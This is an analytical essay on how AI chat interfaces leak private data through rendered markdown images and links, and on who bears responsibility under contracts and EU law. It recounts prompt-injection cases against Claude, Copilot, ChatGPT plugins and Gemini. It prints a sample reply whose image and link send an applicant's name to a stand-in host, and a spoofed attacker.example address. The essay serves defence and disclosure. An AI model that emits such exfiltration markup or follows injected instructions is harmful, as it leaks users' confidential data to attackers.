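An attack on Claude's web-fetching tool shows why the timing matters. The tool could open addresses the user had typed, addresses a search had returned, and links on pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul built a site that asked Claude to find the user's profile by following links letter by letter. In doing so, Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Every address had appeared on a page before Claude opened it, but Paul had supplied those pages. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links on fetched pages.

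An integrator who needs pictures from the web can download every image in a search result before the model reads the text, and have the application show its own copies. The outside server then receives the same requests whichever images the model chooses, so the requests don't reveal the choice. The drawback is that the application downloads many pictures nobody will see.

### Asking the user first

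When an address might carry private data, OpenAI either blocks the request or shows the user what ChatGPT would send and asks for confirmation. Showing the data is better than asking whether the user trusts the site, because the recruiter would recognise Jane Doe's name but might never have heard of images.example. Showing the data works less well if the attacker has encoded it, and a dialog doesn't protect a user who always clicks "yes". Blocking is the better default when the user didn't ask for a picture.

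### One reply in five configurations

Suppose the model returns these four lines to the hiring assistant:

```
Ten years' experience in sales.
![Salary chart](https://images.example/p.png?d=Jane%20Doe)
[Full profile](https://images.example/cv?d=Jane%20Doe)
<script>alert(1)</script>
```

The result depends on the code that displays them. The last three configurations use react-markdown.

| Configuration | What the browser displays | What the browser requests |
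|---|---|---|
| Plain text | All four lines as the model wrote them | Nothing |
| Server-side renderer that passes raw HTML through | The sentence, a picture, a link and an alert box | The image at once, and the link on a click |
| react-markdown with default settings | The sentence, a picture, a link and the script tag as text | The image at once, and the link on a click |
| react-markdown with the CSP `img-src 'self'` | The same, but with a broken image | The link on a click |
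| harden-react-markdown with default settings | The sentence, "[Image blocked: Salary chart]", "Full profile [blocked]" and the script tag as text | Nothing |

Adding DOMPurify to the second configuration would remove the script but not the image.

The third and fourth configurations produce the same HTML, but only the fourth prevents the leak. A reviewer can't tell them apart from the HTML and has to check the browser's network log. The fourth works only if the server sends the CSP with every page that shows a reply. If a developer adds a page without it, the image loads there.

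### What libraries do by default

unified's *react-markdown* describes the library as "secure by default". This is true of scripts, because it displays raw HTML as text and removes `javascript:` addresses. But it permits every element that markdown can produce, including images from any web server. A developer who reads "secure" as covering data leaks would be wrong.

Vercel publishes two tools with opposite defaults. The add-on harden-react-markdown blocks all external links and images until the developer lists which ones to allow, while Streamdown allows them all. In November 2026 Streamdown's documentation carried a prominent warning for developers building chat interfaces, but a safe default would also protect those who don't read the warning.

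Markstream is another library for streamed replies. Its *Security* documentation explains that the default "safe" mode still loads ordinary outside images. It recommends a CSP, an image proxy, a custom image component or a mode that displays HTML as text. The last option may not be enough, because markdown can include an image without any HTML.

Developers also need to check the sample code they copy. TanStack offers a function that is supposed to permit only images the application has validated. For any other image, however, the function applies the library's normal policy, which accepts ordinary web addresses, so an image from images.example would still load. To block it, the function has to return `null` for every image that isn't on the approved list.

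Similarly, one example in Streamdown's *Link Safety* replaces the default processing steps with a list that omits the sanitiser, although Streamdown's security page tells developers always to include it. The example also omits a setting, and the security page says the filter stops with an error without it. A developer who fixes only that error would still have no sanitiser.

### A minimal safe configuration

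An integrator who uses react-markdown and doesn't need pictures in replies can block them with one setting:

```jsx
<Markdown disallowedElements={['img']}>{reply}</Markdown>
```

The server should also send this header with the page:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'
```

`img` is the only element produced by ordinary markdown that makes the browser fetch something without a click. The first line removes it, and react-markdown already displays raw HTML as text. The header restricts the browser to loading images, scripts, styles and fonts from the application's own site, so it also blocks external images inserted by other components. The link in the four-line reply would still work.

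Applications that depend on other hosts need to add them to the header. Plugins need to be checked separately, especially rehype-raw, which turns HTML in the reply back into live elements. The unified project recommends it only for trusted text.

If the hiring assistant has to show its own charts, Streamdown's `allowedImagePrefixes` setting can permit images from a single folder, such as `https://hiring.example/charts/`. The setting covers both markdown images and raw image tags. Nothing in that folder should redirect or fetch other addresses.

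### Filtering a reply while it streams

A chunk of a streamed reply may end partway through an address. Suppose a filter permits any address that begins with `https://hiring.example`, and the first chunk ends there. The filter approves it, but the next chunk adds `.attacker.example/p.png`, so the full address belongs to a different site. A renderer that loads unfinished addresses could also send several requests, each containing a little more of Jane Doe's record.

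The filter has to wait until each image is complete, and the renderer must not create the image before then. Waiting for the whole reply is too late if the page is already displaying it, as happened with Copilot.

Streamdown's *Unterminated Block Parsing* describes one way to handle an image whose address is still arriving. While the address is incomplete, Streamdown replaces it with a placeholder that makes no web request, and the user sees a loading animation. Once the closing bracket arrives, the normal rules apply to the full address. This adds almost no delay, but it offers no protection if those rules permit every host.

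The filter should also check the elements the renderer has created, not the markdown text. Markdown lets an author write `![Salary chart][1]` and give the address for `[1]` many lines later, so a text search for an image followed immediately by an address misses it. Copilot's filter missed this kind of notation in EchoLeak. After conversion, the image element contains the full address however the model wrote it.

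### What remains after images are blocked

The main remaining route is a link that the user clicks. Google's Gemini does not display external images, but Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* showed that links in Gemini's output could still carry private data. In October 2025, Google closed the report as infeasible to fix, four days after receiving it. Gemini removes links to sites that Google knows are malicious, but an attacker can register a new domain.

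Streamdown shows the full address in a dialog before it opens a link. Claude does the same when a small app embedded in a conversation tries to open one, although Anthropic lets apps listed in its directory specify trusted destinations that skip the dialog. Code that makes such exceptions should compare the whole host name. Streamdown's sample code skips the dialog for any address that begins with `https://github.com`, which includes `https://github.com.attacker.example`.

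Reddy and Gujral recommend removing or normalising the part of a link after the question mark, where attackers usually put the data. But an attacker can put it in the path or host name instead. A stronger option is to have the model cite sources by number and let the code attach the addresses of the documents it retrieved. The recruiter can still open the sources, but the model can't write an address of its own.

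Link previews can fetch a URL without a click. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw was exposed to this by default when people used it through Telegram. According to *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024), an integrator whose assistant posts to Slack can turn previews off by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false in each message.

A copy of the reply may also reach a renderer that the integrator doesn't control. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* reports that OpenAI's own log viewer loaded an image that the application had blocked. Showing the reply as plain text, sanitising it or setting a CSP in the application made no difference, because the log held the reply as the model had written it. If an application removed the image, the user might mark the oddly empty answer as bad, which would give a developer a reason to open the log. OpenAI reopened the report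 in January 2026 and said it was working on a fix.

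## Who is responsible: model provider, integrator or interface author

In the log viewer case, the integrator had blocked the hostile image, but OpenAI's own page loaded it. In most of the earlier cases, the integrator's page loaded such an image. Responsibility involves four separate questions, which can have different answers: who caused the flaw, who can fix it most easily, who has promised to fix it, and who is legally liable for the harm.

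Jane Doe's record leaked because the candidate wrote the hidden line, the model followed it, and the integrator's renderer loaded the image. All three were necessary, so causation alone doesn't single out one responsible party. The candidate deserves most of the blame as the only one who meant harm, but blaming the candidate doesn't protect the next applicant. Prevention depends more on who can avoid the harm at the least expense, the party legal scholars call the "cheapest cost avoider". Integrators, model providers and interface authors each have some claim to being that party.

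### The case for the integrator

The case for making the integrator responsible is that it controls the renderer, knows which data is private, and can enforce a rule in code.

Control of the renderer is the strongest reason to hold the integrator responsible. The API returns a string, which can't contact a server until the integrator's code turns it into HTML. An integrator who uses react-markdown can block images with one setting. The model provider can't make that change to the integrator's page, however well it trains the model.

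Some integrators don't control the page, though. The builder of a GPT, a customised version of ChatGPT, supplies instructions and files, but OpenAI's front end displays the replies. OpenAI's *Service terms*, updated on November 13, 2026, still make the builder "solely responsible" for output based on those materials. A builder whose GPT leaked data through an image could not fix the renderer. An integrator whose assistant replies through Slack has partial control, because Slack fetches the link previews that PromptArmor warned about but the integrator can turn them off.

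These cases show that whoever controls the page should be responsible, even if another party is called the integrator. That is the integrator for a hiring assistant on its own website and OpenAI for a GPT.

The second reason to hold the integrator responsible is that the hiring assistant's developers know applicants' records are confidential. The provider receives those records mixed with everything else in the prompt and can't reliably tell a real social security number from an invented one in a training manual. But many integrators don't know what is private either, because users of a general chat product may paste in a medical letter or connect a mailbox. The argument doesn't depend on the integrator knowing this, because a renderer can refuse all unknown hosts without identifying which text is private.

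Display code can enforce the same rule on every reply, whereas an attack that fails against a model many times may still succeed once. However, integrators often get this code wrong, as Writer and Superhuman did with their lists of permitted hosts. Even a company with a good safeguard may not use it everywhere. Embrace The Red warned in 2026 that some developers at OpenAI might not know about the company's own check on web addresses. A two-person company building on another company's model is even less likely to know about such a check.

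An integrator who displays no outside images does not need to keep a list, so the code can be simple. But integrators have to know that the problem exists, and a model provider is well placed to tell them.

### The case for the model provider

The candidate's attack fails if the model ignores the hidden line, so the provider could have prevented the leak too. Providers can clearly affect how often such attacks succeed, since some models in the public competition resisted far more of them than others. But no provider has stopped every attack, and nobody knows how to, so it is more reasonable to expect providers to test their models, publish the results and keep improving them. That would help an integrator choose a model, but it wouldn't fix a page that renders model output unsafely.

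A provider could also change the text that leaves its API, since many models write markdown by default. Microsoft did something similar in 2023 on Azure AI Playground, a page for trying out models. According to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, the fix apparently inserted a space between the brackets of a markdown image, so the page no longer treated it as an image. If a provider offered this as an API setting, the hiring assistant would receive harmless text even if its developers didn't know about image leaks.

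The provider couldn't impose such a setting on everyone, because some customers use models to write documents that need pictures. It also doesn't know which renderer will display the text. An image written as an HTML tag, or with its address given several lines later, would need a separate rule. Integrators would therefore still need a safe renderer. The setting would help most if it were on by default, because the integrators who know least about the problem are the least likely to look for it.

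A better argument for a provider's duty is that a provider serves thousands of integrators and could easily reach many of them with one clear warning. OpenAI's *Safety best practices*, a guide for developers, recommends content moderation, adversarial testing, limits on user input and human review, but it has no advice on how to display a reply safely.

Some of OpenAI's advice also does little to prevent this leak. The company recommends that a person review outputs before using them, but in a chat product the browser has already requested the image by the time the person can review the reply. Limiting what the recruiter can type, which OpenAI also recommends, doesn't affect the text of an uploaded CV.

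OpenAI gives separate advice for Agent Builder, its tool for assembling AI agents. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration in OpenAI Agent Builder via MCP* lists the recommendations, which are to use human oversight, recent models, structured outputs and a feature called Guardrails, and to keep untrusted text out of the developer's own instructions. PromptArmor bypassed a Guardrails step with an injection. Structured outputs, which make the model fill in fixed fields, come closest to a rendering defence. A renderer can treat a field for years of experience as a number, but a free-text summary field can still contain an image.

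OpenAI also supplies a starter app for ChatKit, its kit for building chat interfaces. PromptArmor found that this app had no defence against unsafe images, and neither did ChatKit Playground or the preview pages where developers test agents and assistants before release. The starter app's lack of defence is the clearest failing on the provider's side, because OpenAI wrote the app for other developers to build on and it can be fixed without solving prompt injection.

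### The case for interface and library authors

An interface author can protect every deployment with one safe default. ChatGPT's plugins from outside developers showed the value of this in 2023, when OpenAI was the interface author. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* describes an injection that told ChatGPT to use any available plugin to document the whole conversation. The plugin returned a link to the result, in one case a video with the conversation in its subtitles, and ChatGPT leaked the link through an image.

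The attacker needed the plugin because it could hold far more text than an image address could, and needed the image to learn where the plugin had put the text. A plugin that makes videos on request is working normally, and its author can't control how ChatGPT displays the link. OpenAI could have blocked this route for every such plugin by changing one renderer. Embrace The Red complained that OpenAI was leaving security to plugin developers and users, and recommended handling it in the platform.

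The main objection to holding interface authors responsible is that many of them are volunteers. LibreChat's MIT licence, like most open-source licences, provides the software "as is" and disclaims liability. Someone who publishes a free markdown library for blogs has promised nothing to a recruitment agency that uses it. Blocking images from other sites by default would also be wrong for the library's main users, because it would break many blogs.

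That excuse is weaker for a company that makes an AI chat library. Vercel tells developers to sanitise model output before rendering it, yet only one of its two markdown tools blocks external images by default.

Interface authors also worry that strict defaults will break existing installations, which is why LibreChat leaves its CSP off. If a strict default blocks pictures, though, the administrator will probably notice within a day and can then permit the host, whereas a data leak may never be noticed. Strict defaults therefore seem better for software that displays model output, even if they break some installations.

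An unpaid author can at least describe the software accurately. If "secure by default" refers only to scripts, adding a sentence to say that it doesn't cover images would take little effort.

### Sharing the responsibility

Cloud companies often describe security as a shared responsibility, in which the provider protects the data centre and the customer protects what it runs there. The same view suits chat products, since several parties can each stop the leak. But each can also blame another. The provider can say that the integrator should have blocked the image, the integrator can say that the library's authors called it secure, and those authors can say that their documentation included a warning.

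"Everyone is responsible" therefore assigns no definite duty. Sharing works only if each party has a task that an outsider can check.

| Party | Task | How to check it |
|---|---|---|
| Whoever runs the page that displays the reply | Block requests to unapproved hosts | Display an image from a test server and read the server's log |
| Model provider | Make its own playgrounds, log viewers and starter apps safe, and warn developers about rendering | Repeat the image test on those pages and read the developer guide |
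| Author of an interface or library for AI chat | Block outside images by default | Install it without changing any settings and repeat the test |
| Organisation that installs someone else's interface | Apply updates and protective settings | Compare the version with the latest release and repeat the test |

The party that runs the page, which in most commercial products is the integrator, should have the main responsibility. Its fix stops the image leak even if the model follows the injection and the library has a poor default. It shouldn't be able to excuse an unsafe page by saying that the model should have ignored the CV.

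Responsibility is hardest to assign for a self-hosted interface. The deployer runs the page but may not be able to read its code, and the author, who understands the code, may be a volunteer. The deployer can run the image test without reading the code. If the test fails and no setting fixes the problem, the deployer can only add a content security policy (CSP) at the web server, turn off markdown or choose other software. A small charity might not manage any of these, in which case making it responsible wouldn't protect its users.

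The user isn't in the table because the recruiter can't see the hidden line or the browser's request. It's reasonable to ask the recruiter to be careful with a suspicious link, but not with an image that loads by itself.

### How vendors have classified reports

Companies have often treated leaks through images as someone else's responsibility, or not as a security problem at all. The reports below concern such leaks, except for the one about Gemini's links and the one about ChatGPT's page summaries, which also covered tracking and phishing.

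| Product | Reported | Answer | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | April 9, 2023 | Won't fix | First protection in December 2023 |
| Claude | July 12, 2023 | Confirmed on July 18 | Closed on July 26 after a fix |
| Azure AI Playground | July 24, 2023 | Accepted | Fixed by September 13 |
| Gemini | October 5, 2025 | Won't fix (infeasible) | Closed without a fix |
| Copilot Chat | October 15, 2025 | Not a vulnerability | Closed without a fix |
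| OpenAI's log viewer | November 17, 2025 | Not applicable | Reopened on January 22, 2026 |
| ChatGPT page summaries | April 29, 2026 | Not reproducible, then not applicable, then a duplicate | Researchers published on May 29 |

OpenAI has moved on from its "won't fix" response and now considers automatic leaks through URLs a risk it should prevent in its own products. The company had no bug bounty programme in early 2023, and Rehberger sent the report by email. Rehberger also reported the leak to Microsoft, which added a CSP to Bing Chat in May 2023 to stop images from loading. OpenAI tightened its own check on image URLs around August 2025 and described its method publicly in January 2026.

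The 2023 fixes by Anthropic and Microsoft protected only the pages those companies controlled. A company that used Claude through the API didn't get Anthropic's "Show Image" button on its own page. OpenAI's first check didn't cover even its own mobile apps, because each client had to query the server to find out whether an address was safe. Embrace The Red suggested moving the whole check to the server to protect every client.

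A provider could let its customers' front ends use its address check. OpenAI describes its check as part of ChatGPT and its own agents, and also uses it in its Atlas browser and Deep Research feature. An integrator with its own renderer still needs its own protection.

Microsoft's response about Copilot Chat is the clearest example of a vendor putting the risk on users. Checkmarx, which sells application security tools, demonstrated that an image could leak a secret key from a developer's environment. Microsoft replied on November 4, 2025, that the attack needed several unusual user actions, didn't work reliably in every environment, and came with warnings. It also cited "Workplace Trust", an assumption that people review and trust the code they choose to run.

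The first three reasons are relevant if they are true. Checkmarx itself says that getting the agent to read a hostile page can be somewhat complex, and a recorded demonstration can't show how reliably an attack works. The trust argument is less convincing, because an online article isn't code the user has chosen to run, and a careful reader may still miss hidden instructions. Microsoft did pass the report to its engineers to consider making the behaviour clearer to users.

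Microsoft has fixed similar leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot, so its answer on Copilot Chat isn't a general policy that image leaks don't matter.

Google gave Checkmarx two reasons for rejecting the report about Gemini's links. It marked the report "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", but wrote in its final message that the issue wasn't severe enough to track as a security bug. A leak can be hard to fix and still be severe, so the status alone doesn't show how seriously Google took the risk.

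Outside companies reject some vulnerability reports on a vendor's behalf. OpenAI told PromptArmor that it hadn't seen the log viewer report because Bugcrowd, a company that sorts vulnerability reports for its clients, had handled it. PromptArmor had supplied a step-by-step demonstration and answered questions on three separate days before the case was closed. PromptArmor acknowledges that prompt injection reports are hard to fit into existing categories.

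Permiso also submitted its report on ChatGPT's page summaries through Bugcrowd. OpenAI first said that the report lacked the detail needed to reproduce the problem. After Permiso sent more, the report's label changed to "Not Applicable" and later to duplicate. A duplicate label means that someone had already reported the issue, not that OpenAI agreed to fix it. Bounty programmes use these labels to handle reports, and the labels are poor evidence of who should fix a renderer.

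### What providers' contracts assign

The May 2025 version of OpenAI's services agreement makes the customer "solely responsible for all use of the Outputs" and requires the customer to evaluate whether the output is accurate and appropriate for its purpose. For the hiring assistant, the customer is the integrator.

If Jane Doe brought a claim against OpenAI over the hiring assistant, the integrator would have to defend OpenAI and cover any damages. If the integrator had a claim against OpenAI, the agreement would generally cap OpenAI's total liability at what the integrator had paid in the previous 12 months, with exceptions such as gross negligence. The agreement gives no rights to outsiders like Jane Doe.

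OpenAI promises in its agreement to follow its published security measures, and the agreement defines its services to include developer tools and websites. The log viewer therefore seems to be OpenAI's responsibility under the contract as well as in practice. Features that OpenAI labels as beta don't get the same promise.

OpenAI also offers to cover claims about a model's output, but only claims of intellectual property infringement. A customer can lose that protection by ignoring OpenAI's filtering or safety features. OpenAI makes no equivalent promise to cover a data leak.

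Anthropic put a similar duty on integrators in its commercial terms of May 2024. Before using or sharing outputs, customers must evaluate whether the outputs are appropriate for their use and whether a person should review them. The same clause appears in Anthropic's July 2025 terms for US government customers and in its terms for schools.

These clauses include no instruction to restrict image hosts. "Appropriate" most naturally describes the content of the reply, not how the browser handles it. The integrator has agreed to carry a risk that the contract doesn't describe.

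Model providers can set specific rules for how customers display output. Google Cloud's *Additional Terms for Generative AI Preview Products* required customers who used answers based on Google Search to display them with Google's search suggestions, and only to the person who had asked. A provider could just as easily forbid customers to load images from unknown hosts. It might not be able to check every customer's page, but customers would at least learn about the problem from the clause.

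Mistral's responsibility depends on how a company gets the model. It released Nemo's weights under the Apache 2.0 licence, which makes users solely responsible for determining whether their use is appropriate. When a company runs Nemo on its own server, the replies don't pass through any Mistral service that could filter them. Mistral also made Le Chat, so it controlled the page that displayed Le Chat's replies, but it had no control over the company's page.

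Users of a provider's own products may also take on responsibility. OpenAI's November 2026 terms make users of its agentic features responsible for "content they share on your behalf". If that phrase covered image requests, users would be responsible for leaks they never saw. A clause like this can shift a loss to users without giving them any way to prevent it.

### The EU Cyber Resilience Act

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act sets security rules for "products with digital elements", which include software. Most duties fall on the manufacturer, meaning whoever develops a product, or has it developed, and markets it under its own name. For a desktop chat client, this is normally the integrator, not the model provider.

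Since September 11, 2026, manufacturers have had to report vulnerabilities in their products that attackers are actively exploiting. They must send an early warning within 24 hours of learning about the exploitation, a fuller notice within 72 hours, and a final report within 14 days after a fix or other remedy becomes available. The reports go to a national incident response team and to ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency. Manufacturers must also inform affected users. The duty covers products already on the market.

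The rule applies only when there is reliable evidence that a malicious actor has used the flaw, so a researcher's demonstration doesn't count. Because victims rarely notice image leaks, the rule may produce few reports about them. But an integrator that found Jane Doe's number in a request from its desktop client to the candidate's server would probably have to send the first warning within a day.

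How the Act applies to hosted chat products is less clear. It covers remote processing that a product needs to work, if the manufacturer designed it or is responsible for its design. This includes the manufacturer's own servers behind a desktop or mobile app. A model rented from another company probably doesn't count as part of the integrator's product, because the integrator didn't direct its development.

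The Act's recitals, which explain its purpose and help courts interpret it, exclude websites that don't support a product the Act covers. For cloud services, they refer to a separate EU law, the NIS2 Directive. On that reading, a chat product that exists only as a web page is outside the Act. One could argue that the Act still applies, because the page sends JavaScript that runs on the user's computer, as an installed program does. If web-only products are excluded, a company might have to report a leak in its mobile app but not the same leak on its website.

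The Act doesn't apply to free and open-source software supplied outside a commercial activity, so a volunteer who publishes a free markdown library has no duty to report. Organisations that give sustained support to open-source software intended for commercial use, which the Act calls "stewards", have lighter duties, and regulators can't fine them. A company that sells open-source software is an ordinary manufacturer. Projects such as Dify, which has both free and enterprise editions, are harder to classify, because the free edition's status depends on whether supplying it is part of the company's business.

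From December 11, 2027, manufacturers will also have to supply products with a secure default configuration and take care when choosing components, including free ones. A company that sells a chat interface with no CSP and unrestricted image loading may then struggle to justify those defaults.

### The new Product Liability Directive

Under the EU's new Product Liability Directive, an injured person can claim compensation without proving that a company was careless, but must generally prove that the product was defective and caused the damage. The directive applies through each member state's national law to products placed on the market or put into service after December 9, 2026.

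This directive covers software, and its recitals expressly include software used through the cloud. The integrator would normally be the manufacturer of a hosted hiring assistant. The model provider could also be liable as the manufacturer of a component. The provider has a defence if the defect came from the design of the integrator's product, and it would have a good argument for that defence if the product's renderer loads every image.

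The law is unsettled on whether a model is itself defective because it follows an injected instruction. Courts will consider what safety people are entitled to expect, and no provider can offer a model that resists every injection. It is easier to argue that a page is defective when one setting would have made it safe.

The attacker's part in the harm doesn't reduce the manufacturer's liability to the injured person, and a company can't exclude that liability by contract. Clauses like OpenAI's could still affect how the companies divide the cost afterwards.

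The directive will rarely help victims of image exfiltration like Jane Doe because of the type of damage they suffer. It covers death, physical injury, medically recognised psychological harm, damage to property, and the destruction or corruption of data not used for professional purposes. Image exfiltration copies her number without destroying it, and the recitals distinguish data leaks from destroyed data. They also state that a privacy infringement doesn't create liability by itself.

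The directive does cover some damage that script execution can cause. If a script from a model's reply deleted someone's personal notes, that person could have a claim. The recruiter's candidate files wouldn't qualify, because they are professional data.

The directive also exempts free software supplied outside a commercial activity. If an integrator builds a free library into a commercial product, the integrator can be liable for a defect in the library, but the volunteer who wrote it is not. Integrators therefore have a legal as well as a practical reason to test the renderer they choose.

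The start date is also hard to apply to hosted products, because a chat service that launched in 2024 and changes every week has no obvious date on which its current version reached the market. A substantial modification can count as a new product, but courts will have to decide whether a new model or renderer qualifies.

If Jane Doe lived in the EU, she would more likely claim under the General Data Protection Regulation, which allows compensation for damage caused by a breach of its rules, including non-material damage such as distress. The recruiter's employer would normally be the controller, which decides why and how to use applicants' data, and the integrator would usually be its processor, which handles the data on the employer's behalf. If the weak security breached the regulation, she could claim against the employer, which would escape liability only by proving that it was in no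 way responsible. The employer could then try to recover the money from the integrator.
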